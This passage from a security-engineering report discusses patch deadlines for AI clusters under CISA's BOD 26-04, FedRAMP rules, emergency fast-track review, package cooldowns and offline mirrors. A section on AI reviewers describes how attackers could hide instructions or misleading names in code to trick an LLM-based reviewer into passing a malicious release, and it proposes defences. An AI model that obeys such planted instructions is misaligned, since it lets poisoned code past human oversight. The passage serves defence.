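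The fixes came out on schedule, and CISA told everyone to install them immediately, although it had not yet seen any exploitation (gHale, 2026, *Patch PHP Vulnerabilities Now*). Many attempts followed, but very few succeeded. GreyNoise's *PHP2SHELL Activity 2026* (2026) counted 209,276 attempts on the company's sensors by 28 October and two successes, both from one address that day. The AI company Perplexity had caught a successful attack on its own honeypots a few days earlier, apparently the first (Jones, 2026, *CISA, security researchers confirm successful exploitation of PHP flaws*). Two large security firms, Sophos and Palo Alto Networks, announced successful attacks and then retracted the claims. One explanation in Tsai's collection is that the exploit must hit the same slot in the server's memory repeatedly, which works on a quiet test machine but not on a busy server, where other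 requests keep changing the order.

On 25 October the firm Dream found traces of what looked like a Chinese, AI-assisted campaign that had taken full control of 25 servers, some of them in a US government-affiliated environment. *PHP2Shell breach hits US government-linked network* (Corvin, 2026) apparently describes the same campaign and reports 24 compromised firewalls. The attackers had combined PHP2Shell with a second exploit against the operating system's kernel.

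CISA added both flaws to the KEV catalog on the evening of 26 October and gave civilian agencies until 29 October to patch. By then, more than 10 million of 42 million internet-facing PHP services had the fix, according to *CISA warns of PHP bug exploitation attempts* (Greig, 2026). CISA would not say what exploitation it had seen, and its rules count attempts as well as successes. In December, Irei (2026) asked in *PHP2Shell postmortem* whether the industry had overreacted. For an ordinary website, a week's delay probably did no harm in most cases. But operators of a cluster that holds model weights have to worry about the sort of attacker who ran the campaign that Dream found, and the flaws clearly worked for that attacker.

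A cluster that ran PHP behind a public web page and kept the fix in staging for 14 days would have stayed vulnerable until 4 November, by which time Perplexity, Dream and GreyNoise had all recorded successful attacks. Installing the fix within three days, by 24 October, would have removed the vulnerability at about the time of the first confirmed success. That would still have been too late to stop whoever was active on 17 October, so the operators would also have had to check for an earlier break-in.

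### CISA's four questions

On 10 June 2026, CISA issued Binding Operational Directive 26-04, which federal civilian agencies must follow. An older directive, BOD 19-02, gave agencies 15 days to fix critical flaws on internet-facing systems and 30 days to fix high-severity ones, as rated by CVSS, a severity score from 0 to 10. DePinto and Wang note that the new directive revokes BOD 19-02 and no longer relies mainly on CVSS. The stated aim of CISA's *BOD 26-04* (2026) is to concentrate on the riskiest flaws and put off the rest.

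The deadline depends on four yes-or-no questions. CERT/CC's *HOW TO USE THE CISA RESPONSE TIMELINE SSVC DECISION TREE* defines them roughly as follows:

- Can anyone untrusted or not logged in reach the machine over a public network? If so, it is "publicly exposed", wherever it physically sits.
- Is the flaw in the KEV catalog?
- Can attackers reliably automate the first four steps of an attack: finding targets, preparing the exploit, delivering it and triggering it?
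- Does the exploit give total control of the vulnerable software, or disclose everything on the system? If not, the impact is "partial".

CISA publishes answers to the last three for every CVE number, so an agency only has to work out which of its machines are exposed. The four answers give 16 combinations:

| Publicly exposed | Automatable | Impact | Deadline if not in KEV | Deadline if in KEV |
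|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | Total | 3 days | 3 days and forensic check |
| Yes | Yes | Partial | 14 days | 3 days |
| Yes | No | Total | 14 days | 3 days and forensic check |
| Yes | No | Partial | 60 days | 14 days |
| No | Yes | Total | 60 days | 3 days and forensic check |
| No | Yes | Partial | 60 days | 14 days |
| No | No | Total | Next upgrade | 14 days |
| No | No | Partial | Next upgrade | 14 days |

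"Next upgrade" means the machine's next scheduled major upgrade or rebuild. Deadlines are in calendar days, so a three-day deadline that starts on a Friday ends on Monday.

For a machine off the internet, KEV status matters most. An unlisted flaw on such a machine never has a deadline shorter than 60 days, but a listing cuts the deadline from 60 days to three if the flaw is automatable and gives total control. CISA apparently expects attackers to get past the perimeter sometimes, but it waits for evidence that they are using the flaw before it shortens the deadline.

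The PHP flaws show how much a patching deadline can depend on whether a flaw is automatable. Their impact is total because they give an attacker control of the PHP process. It is unclear whether they were automatable, because the definition requires reliable automation and almost all of the hundreds of thousands of automated requests attackers sent failed. If the deadline runs from the fix's release, an exposed server had to be patched by 24 October if the flaws were automatable and by 4 November if they were not. Once the flaws were listed in KEV on 26 October, exposed servers had a three-day deadline and needed a forensic check in either case. For an internal dashboard running the same PHP version, the listing would have shortened the deadline from 60 days to three if the flaws were automatable, and from the next upgrade to 14 days if they were not.

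### Checking for a break-in

A fix doesn't remove an attacker who got in before it arrived. For three of the 16 combinations, all of them flaws in KEV with total impact, agencies must therefore also carry out forensic triage, a quick examination of the machine for signs of compromise. CISA's guidance recommends a schedule, which Inside Privacy's *CISA Releases Binding Operational Directive on Prioritizing Security Updates Based on Risk* sets out in hours from the KEV listing:

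| Hours after listing | Work |
|---|---|
| 0–2 | Decide whether the flaw needs triage, call in the response team, and set up communications that don't depend on the affected systems |
| 2–24 | Save the contents of memory and other evidence that a shutdown would erase, then patch |
| 6–24 | Begin to contain affected systems without destroying evidence |
| 24–48 | Look for intruders, spread to other machines, and copied or staged data |
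| 48–72 | Write a report with a timeline, findings and next steps |

The order of steps within the first day matters because installing a fix usually requires a restart, which wipes any evidence in memory. A training node in an AI cluster can hold hundreds of gigabytes in memory, including model weights, so a thief would want a copy of that evidence. The operators need an approved place inside the cluster to store it. They also need someone outside the perimeter to watch the KEV catalog at all hours, since an isolated machine can't check it. CISA listed the PHP flaws on a Monday evening, so the two-hour step would have fallen that night.

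A KEV listing shortens the deadline for a patch, while taking a machine off the internet can lengthen it because the machine is less exposed. An operator can legitimately take a machine offline to gain time when a fix is not ready, as long as the machine really is unreachable.

### FedRAMP's version

FedRAMP, the US programme that certifies cloud services for government use, is adopting the same approach. In June FedRAMP (2026) announced that its new vulnerability rules would become mandatory on 7 December 2026, the day agencies must start meeting the directive's deadlines. It had planned to wait until June 2027. Providers that are not ready can keep their certification under a corrective plan until 7 March 2027, after which FedRAMP will revoke it.

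Two of the rules differ from the directive in ways that could help a cluster operator. A provider must assume that attackers can automate an exploit unless it has evidence that they can't. For the PHP flaws, this would have given an exposed server a three-day deadline from the start, without any argument about memory slots. A provider may also mitigate a flaw so that attackers can no longer automate an exploit or reach the flaw from the internet, and then it doesn't have to fully fix the flaw by the original deadline.

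FedRAMP also stresses that all these periods are maximums. It says the monthly scans that most certified services still rely on are insufficient, because a flaw disclosed the day after a scan could pass both a 3-day and a 14-day deadline before anybody noticed it.

### What else feeds the decision

The directive's table is an SSVC tree. SSVC (Stakeholder-Specific Vulnerability Categorization) is a method for choosing an action from the answers to a few questions about a flaw. It was developed by CERT/CC, a security centre at Carnegie Mellon University. Organizations can build their own trees. CERT/CC's tree for organizations that install patches has three levels of exposure (small, controlled and open) and three levels of exploitation (none, public proof of concept and active). "Public proof of concept" would have suited the PHP flaws between 21 and 26 October, when attackers had published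 exploit code but CISA had not yet listed them.

Teams use three other tools alongside a tree:

| Tool | What goes in | What comes out |
|---|---|---|
| SSVC tree | Answers about the flaw and the machine | An action or a deadline |
| EPSS score | Public data about the flaw, such as its age, its vendor and any exploit code | The probability of exploitation somewhere in the next 30 days |
| Reachability analysis | The operator's own code and its dependencies | Whether the program can reach the flawed code |
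| VEX statement | The supplier's analysis of its own product | Affected, not affected, fixed or under investigation |

EPSS (the Exploit Prediction Scoring System) comes from FIRST, an association of incident response teams, which publishes new scores daily. A score of 0.02 means a 2% chance that somebody's sensors will record an attack on the flaw within 30 days. Low scores add up. If a cluster has 100 unfixed flaws at 1% each, and the chances are independent, the probability that attackers use at least one of them somewhere that month is:

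$$1-(1-0.01)^{100}\approx 0.63$$

So a team can't dismiss a backlog just because every flaw in it has a low score. The score is also the same for every cluster. The model learns from recorded attacks, mostly on internet-connected networks. Neither its training data nor KEV would reflect an exploit that a state agency keeps for a single attack on an isolated cluster.

Reachability analysis depends on the cluster, but people use the term for several tests. DePinto and Wang check only whether the flawed component is running in production. Stricter tools trace calls through the program to see whether any path leads to the flawed function. Such tools could have dismissed many of the unexploitable alerts that Pashchenko and colleagues found in SAP's libraries, but they can miss functions that a program selects while running, for instance through a plugin or a configuration file. A finding that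 no path exists also holds only for the code the tool examined, and in an AI cluster the researchers' code may change every day even when its libraries are pinned.

VEX (Vulnerability Exploitability eXchange) lets a supplier tell everyone who runs its product whether a flaw affects it. If an image-processing package includes a compression library but leaves out the flawed function, the supplier can state that the package is not affected and give the reason in a form that a scanner can read. A "fixed" statement would also stop false alarms about packages with backported fixes, whose version numbers look old. However, the operator has to trust the supplier's analysis, and a forged or careless "not affected" would hide a real flaw. The statements therefore need signatures as much as the software does, and they also have to cross the air gap.

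A sensible order is to start with VEX and reachability, which rule out flaws that can't matter, then use the tree to set deadlines for the rest, and finally use EPSS to choose between flaws due on the same day. For the reason above, a low EPSS score should not justify extending a deadline in an isolated cluster.

### Two flaws in an isolated cluster

Suppose two flaws appear on the same morning, both with fixes available and neither in KEV. One is in the login gateway, the server through which researchers enter the cluster. Anyone who can send it network traffic can take it over without a password and can script the whole attack. The other is in the container runtime, the software that runs programs in isolated compartments on each machine. A program inside a compartment can use the flaw to break out and control the whole machine.

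The gateway accepts connections only from an internal company network, so it is not publicly exposed. Its flaw is automatable and has total impact, so the deadline is 60 days. If the company let researchers connect to it from the internet, the deadline would be three days.

The container runtime is not exposed either. Its flaw has total impact, but an attacker must already be running code in a container to use it, so a reviewer would probably decide that the attack can't be automated. The fix would then wait for the next upgrade, with no deadline in days. In a cluster whose machines are rebuilt once a year, the flaw could remain for up to a year and add up to 365 flaw-days. If CISA later listed both flaws, the gateway would need a fix within three days plus a forensic check, and the runtime would need a fix within 14 days.

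An operator following RAND's 21-day benchmark would fix both unlisted flaws long before the directive required it. But if either flaw were added to the KEV catalog, 21 days would be too slow. The simplest way to use the benchmark and the directive together is to follow whichever deadline is shorter.

### Attackers who are already inside

The container runtime result is hard to defend for this kind of cluster. The exposure question is about outsiders on public networks. That works well for an agency with thousands of servers, because criminals scan the internet for anything they can break into. But an attacker who wants model weights may be an employee, someone using a researcher's stolen account, or an AI agent that runs code in the cluster as part of its job. Containers are a common way to build the confined environments in which the SL5 draft lets AI models run experiments without full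 review, and the invented flaw lets a program escape from its container.

A related weakness is that the table rates each flaw separately, even though attackers can combine them, as they did in Dream's PHP campaign. They got in with PHP2Shell and then used a kernel exploit to gain full control. A reviewer scoring that kind of kernel flaw alone would probably judge it hard to automate, because it is useless to someone who can't already run code on the machine. On an internal machine, the fix could then wait for the next upgrade unless CISA had listed the flaw.

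An operator can correct for this without abandoning the table, by changing what counts as exposed. One option is to treat a component as exposed if anyone or anything that should not have the weights can send it input. Adding FedRAMP's assumption about automation makes the table stricter again. These are the deadlines for the two flaws, with neither in KEV:

| How the operator answers the questions | Login gateway | Container runtime |
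|---|---|---|
| CISA's definitions | 60 days | Next upgrade |
| Untrusted people and programs inside count as exposure | 3 days | 14 days |
| The same, and assume attackers can automate the exploit | 3 days | 3 days |

A broad definition of exposure could make nearly every flaw urgent, because almost every component inside a cluster receives input from some user or program. Reviewers would then rush dozens of fixes a month and be more likely to miss a poisoned update. CISA's narrower definition avoids this by letting most internal flaws wait.

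The broad definition makes most sense for components that separate people and programs with different levels of trust. In a typical cluster, these include the login gateway, the container runtime, the kernel, the service that checks identities, and the system that signs and distributes updates. A plotting library inside a researcher's container doesn't belong on the list, because exploiting it usually gives an attacker only the access that code in the container already has. The list is short enough for a team to maintain by hand and review when the cluster's design changes.

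Reachability analysis needs the same care. Even if a tool finds that the researchers' programs never call a flawed kernel function, an intruder, or an agent writing its own code, can call it directly. For components that confine untrusted code, the operator should not extend the patching deadline because existing programs don't reach the flaw.

### Clusters that the directive does not cover

BOD 26-04 binds only federal civilian agencies. By law it excludes national security systems and certain systems of the Department of War and the intelligence agencies. A presidential memorandum of January 2022, NSM-8, lets the director of the National Security Agency issue binding directives for national security systems, much as CISA does for civilian ones. It also required the two sides to share their directives and consider adopting each other's requirements. The military has its own programme of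 vulnerability alerts, each with a date by which units must comply or file a plan to comply. A classified AI cluster would therefore get its deadlines from those channels, and outsiders may never see them.

Contractors are not directly bound either, unless a contract requires it, although CISA has told agencies to review their contracts with this in mind. An AI company that sells a certified cloud service to the government must follow FedRAMP's rules for that service. Its internal research cluster, where it may keep its most valuable weights, would normally fall under none of these regimes. CISA encourages everyone else to adopt the directive's approach. One of its officials told AFCEA, a military communications association, that the agency publishes its directives partly so that others can use them as best practice.

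The company therefore has to set its own deadlines, and the directive's table is a reasonable source for the number of days that NIST's SI-2 control leaves blank. A flaw then needs an emergency exception if an ordinary update would miss its deadline. If staging takes 14 days and everything else takes seven, an ordinary update arrives on day 21, in time for a 60-day deadline but too late for a 14-day or 3-day one. The operators can shorten staging or hire more reviewers so that fewer fixes need an exception, but a cluster that holds releases for two weeks will always need one to meet a 3-day deadline.

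## Fast-track review of an emergency fix

An emergency exception lets operators change a pinned version early, but they still have to check that the fix is genuine and works. They have two or three days for a process that normally takes three weeks in the example cluster. A fast-track review saves most of the time by shortening the wait in staging and testing less broadly, while keeping the checks that can catch a poisoned release.

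NIST's *Guide to Enterprise Patch Management Planning* (SP 800-40 Revision 4) suggests handling emergency patches much like routine ones, but on a "highly accelerated schedule". It may still help to install the fix first on a few machines, known as canaries, to confirm that the file isn't corrupted and doesn't break the software. The canary period can last from a few minutes to a few hours, and the rest of the rollout can follow over the next hours or days.

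*Design for Recovery*, a chapter by Joyner, McCune and colleagues in a Google engineering book, similarly recommends building an update system that can run as fast as anyone might ever need, then adding limits that slow it down in ordinary times. In an emergency, operators only loosen the limits. A separate emergency system would sit unused for most of the year, and the chapter warns that untested emergency practices don't work when people need them.

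*Patch Fast, But Let It Bake* (Heffner, 2026) describes a fast track for emergency fixes on Heffner's home cluster. The cluster rebuilds its web server image every week, scans and signs it, and keeps it on standby for 72 hours before it serves traffic. A fix for a flaw that attackers are already using can skip the wait but still needs a signature, because the cluster won't run an unsigned image.

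### What to shorten and what to keep

For the example cluster, the two kinds of review might compare like this:

| Step | Ordinary update | Emergency fix |
|---|---|---|
| Check the signature and hash | Yes | Yes |
| Read the code changes | Yes | Yes |
| Approval by two people | Yes | Yes |
| Compile and sign internally | Yes | Yes |
| Functional tests | Full suite, including long training runs | The repaired component and whatever uses it directly |
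| Time in staging | 14 days | A few hours |
| Small first group of machines | A day or more | A few hours |
| Tested way back to the old version | Yes | Yes |

Skipping the signature and hash checks would save only seconds. NIST advises organizations to confirm a patch's authenticity and integrity before testing or installing it, since it may come from a rogue source or someone may have altered it in transit. Reading the code takes much longer, but without the 14-day wait, reviewers can't rely on other users to find malicious code first.

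The narrower tests also risk missing faults that take time to appear. A few hours on test machines will probably reveal a crash, but not a slow memory leak or a small drift in numerical results that only shows up after a week of training. Operators have to accept some of that risk and watch for such faults after the fix is deployed.

Reviewing a fix takes longer the further the cluster's software has fallen behind. NIST points out that delaying routine patches makes emergency patching slower and more disruptive, because a new patch may require earlier ones first. If the cluster runs version 7.3.0 of a program and the fix arrives in 7.3.6, reviewers have to read the changes in all six releases unless someone can backport the fix.

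### Declaring the emergency

A team that starts from scratch with each new flaw will spend the first day debating what to do. NIST says that no organization has the time or staff to do a full risk assessment of every vulnerability, and advises making most of the decisions in advance. Operators sort machines into maintenance groups with similar needs and write a plan for each group that gives a start and end time for every action. For example, login gateways and training nodes would belong to different groups, because restarting a gateway interrupts a few sessions, while restarting a training node can stop a job that uses thousands of chips.

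The operators also have to decide who can start the plan. *Change Management*, the published procedure of the software-hosting company GitLab, covers the hardest case, the year-end holidays, when GitLab locks its production systems and most people are away. During that lock, a change needed for a serious incident requires approval from two people already on duty, the engineer on call and the incident manager. The incident manager then tells senior leadership, but the change doesn't have to wait for them. Exemptions for any other reason need approval from a vice president or a delegate.

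A newly published flaw that nobody has exploited yet could call for either an emergency fix or an ordinary update, so a cluster's operators should decide in advance how to classify such flaws. If an ordinary update would miss the flaw's deadline, the security engineer on duty can declare an emergency and the operations manager on duty can confirm it.

They can approve several other steps in advance, such as cutting staging to a few hours, restarting particular services, calling reviewers in at the weekend and switching on prepared compensating controls. They can't approve the release itself in advance, because nobody has seen it yet. For its riskiest changes, GitLab wants a reviewer from outside the author's team, which is a good rule for the second approval here.

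Requiring a second approval adds little delay to an emergency patch if the second person is available, because the patch already takes a day or two. NIST does advise organizations to consider the risk of requiring dual authorization when they must respond immediately to protect the public or the environment, in text that Thiergart and colleagues reproduce in the SL5 draft. The draft requires at least one custodian with the highest clearance to take part in dual authorization for operations on the weights. It also requires two authorized people to be present in the secured zones at all times. An operator following the draft would therefore need enough cleared staff on the weekend rota, or the patch could be delayed until Monday.

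### Break-glass procedures

Some organizations also have a break-glass procedure, which lets an engineer bypass the normal checks and records the bypass. Google's *Binary Authorization for Borg* describes one for Borg, the system that runs jobs on Google's clusters. Before Borg starts a job, an automatic check confirms that the code and configuration meet the service's policy. By default, the code must come from the approved repository, and Google must be able to trace the program back to its source.

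In an emergency, an engineer can override the check with a special flag and a written justification. The system logs the job, the justification and a reference to a snapshot of the deployed code. It also notifies Google's central security team and the team that owns the service. At least once a day, a separate process looks for jobs that don't meet current policy, including any deployed this way.

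This procedure allows unreviewed code, which makes sense for a company whose first priority in an outage is to restore service. It is a poor fit for a cluster that holds model weights, where unreviewed code can do more damage than a day of downtime. The cluster's operators can borrow the logging, the two notifications and the daily check, but should still require review.

An attacker could also use a break-glass procedure. Another chapter of the same Google book therefore says that every use must raise an alarm and get a quick audit, and that uses must be rare enough for auditors to tell an attack from an honest emergency. Google Cloud's *Defense Evasion*, documentation for a threat detection service, classes a break-glass deployment as a possible attempt to get around security controls. The same caution applies to a fast-track review. If a team declares emergencies too often, reviewers will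 not pay much attention to new ones.

### A 48-hour timetable

Suppose the maintainers of the login gateway release version 7.3.2, which changes about 60 lines to fix a flaw in 7.3.1 that lets anyone who can reach the gateway take it over. Under the stricter definition of exposure, the operators have three days from the release.

| Hours | Work | Reason to stop |
|---|---|---|
| 0–2 | Confirm from the inventory that the cluster runs 7.3.1, declare the emergency, restrict access to the gateway | The cluster doesn't use the flawed feature |
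| 2–5 | Download the release outside the perimeter, check its signature and hash, carry it into quarantine | The signature or hash fails |
| 5–12 | Two reviewers separately read the changes and compare them with the maintainers' source repository | Either reviewer finds a change they can't explain |
| 12–16 | Compile from source, sign with the internal key | The program can't be rebuilt from the reviewed code |
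| 16–24 | Run the short test suite, try the known attack, practise returning to 7.3.1 and back | The attack still works, or logins fail |
| 24–30 | Install on one gateway and watch it | Crashes, or unexpected network connections |
| 30–42 | Install on the other gateways in batches | As above |
| 42–48 | Confirm which version is running, update the gold image, book the full review | A gateway still runs the old version |

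The new version spends eight hours in staging instead of 336. The timetable leaves a spare day before the deadline in case a reviewer is ill or a build fails.

If the review stops, the team still has the access restrictions it placed on the gateway in the first two hours. NIST calls this emergency mitigation and treats it as a separate scenario, for when no patch exists yet or the patch is flawed, disruptive or compromised. NIST advises setting dates for installing the permanent fix and for removing the temporary measure.

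If the flaw also calls for a forensic check, the team has to save the gateway's memory before the restart at hour 24.

The first gateway mainly reveals accidental faults, because a well-made poisoned release would work normally for six hours. Still, NIST notes that monitoring software's behavior after a patch can help detect a compromised one. For example, a login gateway that suddenly contacts a storage server it has never used would need investigating.

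### Cooldown settings and their exemptions

Many teams enforce the waiting period with a cooldown in their package tools, so an emergency fix needs an exemption there too. The security company Socket called the handling of urgent fixes the most contentious part of the cooldown debate, and found that tools tended to give users explicit control.

In pnpm, a package manager for JavaScript, `minimumReleaseAge` sets the wait in minutes, and `minimumReleaseAgeExclude` lists packages that can skip it. uv, for Python, and Bundler, for Ruby, have their own settings for this. Dependabot, a GitHub service, proposes updates but doesn't install them. According to GitHub's *The case for a cooldown*, it now waits at least three days before proposing an ordinary update, but proposes security updates without this delay.

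| Tool | Normal wait | Exception | What skips the wait |
|---|---|---|---|
| pnpm | `minimumReleaseAge` | `minimumReleaseAgeExclude` | The packages or versions on the list |
| uv | `exclude-newer` | `exclude-newer-package` | One package |
| Bundler | `cooldown`, in days | `--cooldown 0` | Everything the command resolves |
| Dependabot | 3 days by default | Automatic | Security updates |

An exemption should cover as little as possible. Kochan's *pnpm 10.17* lets a team exempt a whole family of packages with a pattern such as `@eslint/*`. This is convenient, but any new release in that family can then skip the wait. Kochan's *pnpm 10.19* added exemptions for exact versions, such as `nx@21.6.5`, which are better for a pinned cluster because the reviewers have approved only that version.

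Bundler's zero is the least selective of these settings. An operator who uses it to get one fix should compare the old and new lockfiles to check whether the command also picked up another release from that morning.

Shigeoka (2025), in *How pnpm's minimumReleaseAgeExclude Helped with Emergency Security Updates*, describes his team's response to CVE-2025-55182, a serious flaw in the web library React. Their project required releases to be at least 24 hours old. The developers considered setting the wait to zero but decided against it because somebody might forget to restore it, and other packages might jump to their newest versions in the meantime. Instead, they exempted React and three related packages by name, installed the fix, and later emptied the exemption list, leaving a comment that it was for temporary use in emergencies.

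Dependabot's automatic exemption must also apply in the package manager. For security updates, Dependabot runs the JavaScript package managers pnpm and recent versions of Yarn with a waiting time of zero, so the project's own cooldown doesn't block the fix. If two tools have different waiting times, the build can fail. Classmethod's *pnpm v11 minimumReleaseAge Causes Dependabot CI Failures* describes a case with ordinary updates, in which Dependabot proposed versions less than a day old and pnpm blocked their installation.

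These settings depend on each version's release date, which an offline mirror may not keep. The Python Developer Tooling Handbook's *How to Protect Against Python Supply Chain Attacks with uv* warns that uv's cooldown has no effect on packages from a private index that lacks upload times. Fromager's *Protect Against Supply-Chain Attacks with Release-Age Cooldown* describes a build tool that fails by default if the times are missing, which is safer. In an isolated cluster, it is more reliable to enforce the wait where software enters the mirror and use the settings inside the cluster as a second check.

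### When the resolver hides the fix

A cooldown can also clash with the tool that warns about known flaws. *Dependency cooldowns considered harmful*, an essay that argues against most uses of cooldowns, explains how this happens in a Python project that uses uv. uv's resolver chooses versions and writes the lockfile. The auditor, a separate program called pip-audit, compares the lockfile with a live database of flaws.

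Suppose the maintainers of a library disclose a flaw and release a fix the same day. The resolver ignores the fix because it is too new, so the lockfile still names the vulnerable version. The auditor finds that version listed in its vulnerability database and fails the build. The developer runs the resolver again and gets the same lockfile. Requesting the fixed version directly doesn't help, because the resolver removes recent releases before it applies any version requirements, so it reports that the fixed version doesn't exist.

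With a 14-day cooldown and a three-day deadline, the build would fail for two weeks, and the fix would arrive 11 days late. Developers might well respond by turning off the auditor, which would also hide any other flaws it would detect.

Exempting a single package with `exclude-newer-package` breaks the deadlock, but somebody has to notice the problem and edit the list every time. The essay mentions this exemption later on, but its summary is too strong in saying that no user-level override can rescue a cooldown.

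The essay itself proposes an advisory-aware rule, under which the resolver checks the flaw database and lets a recent release through if it fixes a listed flaw. It says no mainstream Python resolver does this. However, Hex, the package manager for Elixir, has a similar rule. Hex's *Dependency security* says the cooldown doesn't apply to a package whose locked version has a security advisory. It doesn't apply to that version's direct dependencies either, because the fix may need newer versions of them. A cooldown set by a dependency policy still applies, so an organization can keep its wait even for these packages.

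This rule is risky for high-security use because, as Hex describes it, an advisory lifts the cooldown for the whole package, not just for the release that contains the fix. An attacker who had stolen a maintainer's password could wait for a genuine advisory and then publish a malicious version, which would skip the cooldown on everyone's machines. A cluster should use a narrower rule that exempts only the exact version the advisory names as fixed, and should still put that version through the fast-track review.

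An isolated cluster can avoid the deadlock simply because its copy of the flaw database is out of date. If the copy is two weeks old, the auditor will pass a version whose flaw was disclosed since then. Operators should import new advisories daily, even when they import no software.

### One package through the offline mirror

When an emergency arises, an offline mirror may already have dozens of new versions in quarantine. Synchronizing the mirror with the public repository to get the urgent fix would release all of them at once.

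Joyner and colleagues write that Google used to install the same base image on every machine in its data centers and update it once a month. Urgent security patches for individual packages became exceptions to the image, and the list of exceptions grew until the monthly schedule made little sense. Google then split the image so that each package could roll out at its own speed. For an emergency release, operators now adjust some rate limits and approve one type of package to roll out faster than normal.

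A mirror can work the same way if it publishes approved software as numbered snapshots that never change. To add the gateway fix, an operator copies the current snapshot, say number 118, and adds only version 7.3.2, leaving the queued updates in quarantine. The mirror software rebuilds the package index, two people approve the new snapshot, and the signing system signs it as number 119. The operator then points the gateways at 119 and leaves every other machine on 118.

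Comparing the indexes of snapshots 118 and 119 is a simple check. If they differ by more than the gateway package, somebody has made a mistake or tampered with the snapshot, unless the fix requires a newer version of another package, which then has to go through the same review. When a fix brings in more than a few other packages, it is usually better to look for a backport.

Version 7.3.1 should stay in the snapshot until the team is sure of 7.3.2, because the gateways may have to roll back to it. But Joyner and colleagues point out that an attacker can also use a rollback to bring back a known flaw. They suggest a deny list of versions that the system will no longer install. The operators would add 7.3.1 to it once 7.3.2 has proved stable.

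### When the urgent fix is the attack

Attackers could abuse the fast track by labeling a malicious release as an urgent fix. They would first need the right to publish releases, which they are trying to get. In September 2026 the developer Willison passed on a warning from the Rust language's package security team about a campaign targeting people who maintain popular packages. The attackers arrange a video call about a job or a contract, then get the maintainer to install something, such as a supposedly missing audio codec.

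These attacks spread worryingly fast, but it is slightly reassuring that defenders can catch them within hours. In March 2026 somebody published a backdoored version of axios, a JavaScript package with more than a hundred million downloads a week. Heffner reports that it infected the first victim's machine about 89 seconds later. A security company flagged the release within about six minutes, and it was gone in about three hours. GitHub reports that poisoned versions of chalk, debug and other packages lasted roughly two hours in September 2025.

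In the timetable above, a release is at least 24 hours old before it reaches the first production machine. The time spent on review and testing therefore also serves as a short cooldown, which would have been long enough to outlast all of these attacks. The operators only have to check for warnings once more before hour 24. The cooldown is a good reason not to shorten the schedule to six hours unless attackers are already using the flaw against similar systems.

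These packages were very popular, though. *Dependency cooldowns considered harmful* points out that a lack of reported problems is no evidence that a package is safe if nobody is watching it. The same applies if an attack activates only inside one particular cluster.

The most useful check in these cases is to compare the release with the maintainers' source repository. Reviewers find the commit (the recorded change to the source code) labeled as the fix. They check that it changes the code described in the advisory, and that the release contains this change and no others they can't account for. The axios attacker published the release by hand with a stolen token. A release published that way need not match anything in the repository, and a reviewer who compared the two could see the extra code.

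The comparison fails if the attacker also controls the repository, so reviewers should also confirm the flaw through a second source, such as a Linux distribution's security team. If the only evidence of the emergency comes from the account that published the release, they should keep the compensating control in place and wait.

Honest mistakes are more common than attacks. Engineers at Google write that they have often seen hastily deployed fixes fail to solve the problem or make it worse, and that they normally roll back first and investigate afterwards. Rolling back a security fix also restores the flaw, so operators have to switch the compensating control back on first.

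A limit on the size of the change helps rushed reviewers more than any instruction to be careful. Two people can read 60 changed lines properly in seven hours, but they will skim 6,000. The team should refuse to fast-track a release that large and look for a smaller fix.

### AI reviewers

An AI model can read 6,000 lines in minutes, which makes it tempting to raise that limit. A model can help with the review by matching each change in a release to a commit, listing the new network calls, and pointing out code unrelated to the advisory.

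But the attacker can also try to mislead the reviewing model. The SL5 draft (Thiergart et al.) warns that external code may contain "inputs designed to compromise LLM-based code review or hardening systems". The attacker could simply add a comment telling the model that a security team has already approved the file or, more subtly, choose function names and structure that make a harmful change look like part of the repair. The draft requires detection systems to resist attempts to bypass them, but concedes that this is still an unsolved problem.

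It is safest to let a model block a release but never to count its approval as one of the two approvals. An attacker who fools the model then only suppresses a warning. This only works if the human reviewers read the files themselves before they see the model's result, since people told that a file is clean will read it less carefully.

The model should also run in quarantine, without credentials or a route into the cluster, because a model that follows hidden instructions and can sign packages is worse than no reviewer. Stripping comments before the model reads the code removes the easiest place to hide instructions, but they can still be hidden in names and text strings.

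### After the emergency

Once the last gateway is running 7.3.2, the team still has to do the work it postponed. Someone who didn't approve the release the first time should run the full test suite, read the changes again without a deadline, and watch for reports about the release until it is 14 days old, when it would have left staging anyway. If this review finds malicious code, the team has to treat the whole period since installation as a break-in, so it should keep detailed logs covering at least that period. A late review can't recover weights that have already been stolen, so it can't replace the reading in hours 5 to 12.

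The first fix may also be incomplete. NIST mentions patches that don't correct the vulnerability. The test at hours 16 to 24 covers only the attacks known at the time, and researchers often look harder at code after someone finds a flaw in it. The team should keep the reviewers available and be ready to send 7.3.3 through the same steps a few days later.

Exemptions cause problems more slowly. *Dependency cooldowns considered harmful* predicts that people will add packages to an exemption list and never remove them, so that within a year the list will cover every security-critical package. The essay offers no data, but the prediction is plausible because an old exemption breaks nothing and triggers no alert. NIST advises tracking all exceptions and reviewing them regularly.

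An expiry date works better than a reminder for removing a cooldown exemption, and the right date is easy to calculate. An exemption for one exact version is no longer needed once that version is old enough to pass the normal wait. If 7.3.2 came out on 1 June and the wait is 14 days, the exemption can expire on 15 June. *cooldown-guard*, a small tool for uv, limits each exception to one version, records who approved it, the reason and the advisory, and ends it automatically once the version has passed the normal wait.

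The team must also pin the new version. If the main lockfile still specifies 7.3.1, the next routine rebuild will bring the flaw back, and a restored backup may too. The team should update the lockfile and the gold image, move all machines to a regular snapshot that includes the fix, and then close the exception.

Teams need to practice all of this. Heffner nearly locked himself out of his cluster when he made signatures mandatory, because the image already running predated signing and could not have restarted. He had to deploy a signed image first. A team with a cluster full of training jobs should find such problems on a quiet day, by sending a harmless update through the fast track every few months and timing each step. At least one rehearsal should start on a Saturday, when the second approver is hardest to reach.

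## Applying a fix without a full upgrade

Two reviewers can fast-track a small change, but a fix often arrives inside a large release. OpenSSH 9.8, released on 1 July 2024, fixed a serious race condition in the program that most Linux servers use for remote login. Miller (2024) also posted a minimal patch in *Announce* for people who would rather not upgrade. It adds two lines that tell the compiler to leave out some logging code unless the system can run it safely.

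The full release also split the server into two programs, disabled an old signature algorithm, changed log messages and began to penalize addresses whose logins fail, according to the changelog from Debian (2024). That last change could cause trouble in a cluster where all researchers connect through one gateway and so share an address. Debian's development branch had the small patch on the day of the announcement, according to a changelog entry quoted by Martin (2024). The branch got the full release 30 days later.

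A reviewer can read and understand every line of a twenty-line fix in an hour, and many fixes are shorter. *SoK: From Finding to Deployment* (2026), a study of 6,946 fixed bugs in the Linux kernel, found that the median fix changed five lines in one file. An operator can backport only the fix to the pinned version, which gives an attacker much less room to hide malicious code than a release with months of other changes.

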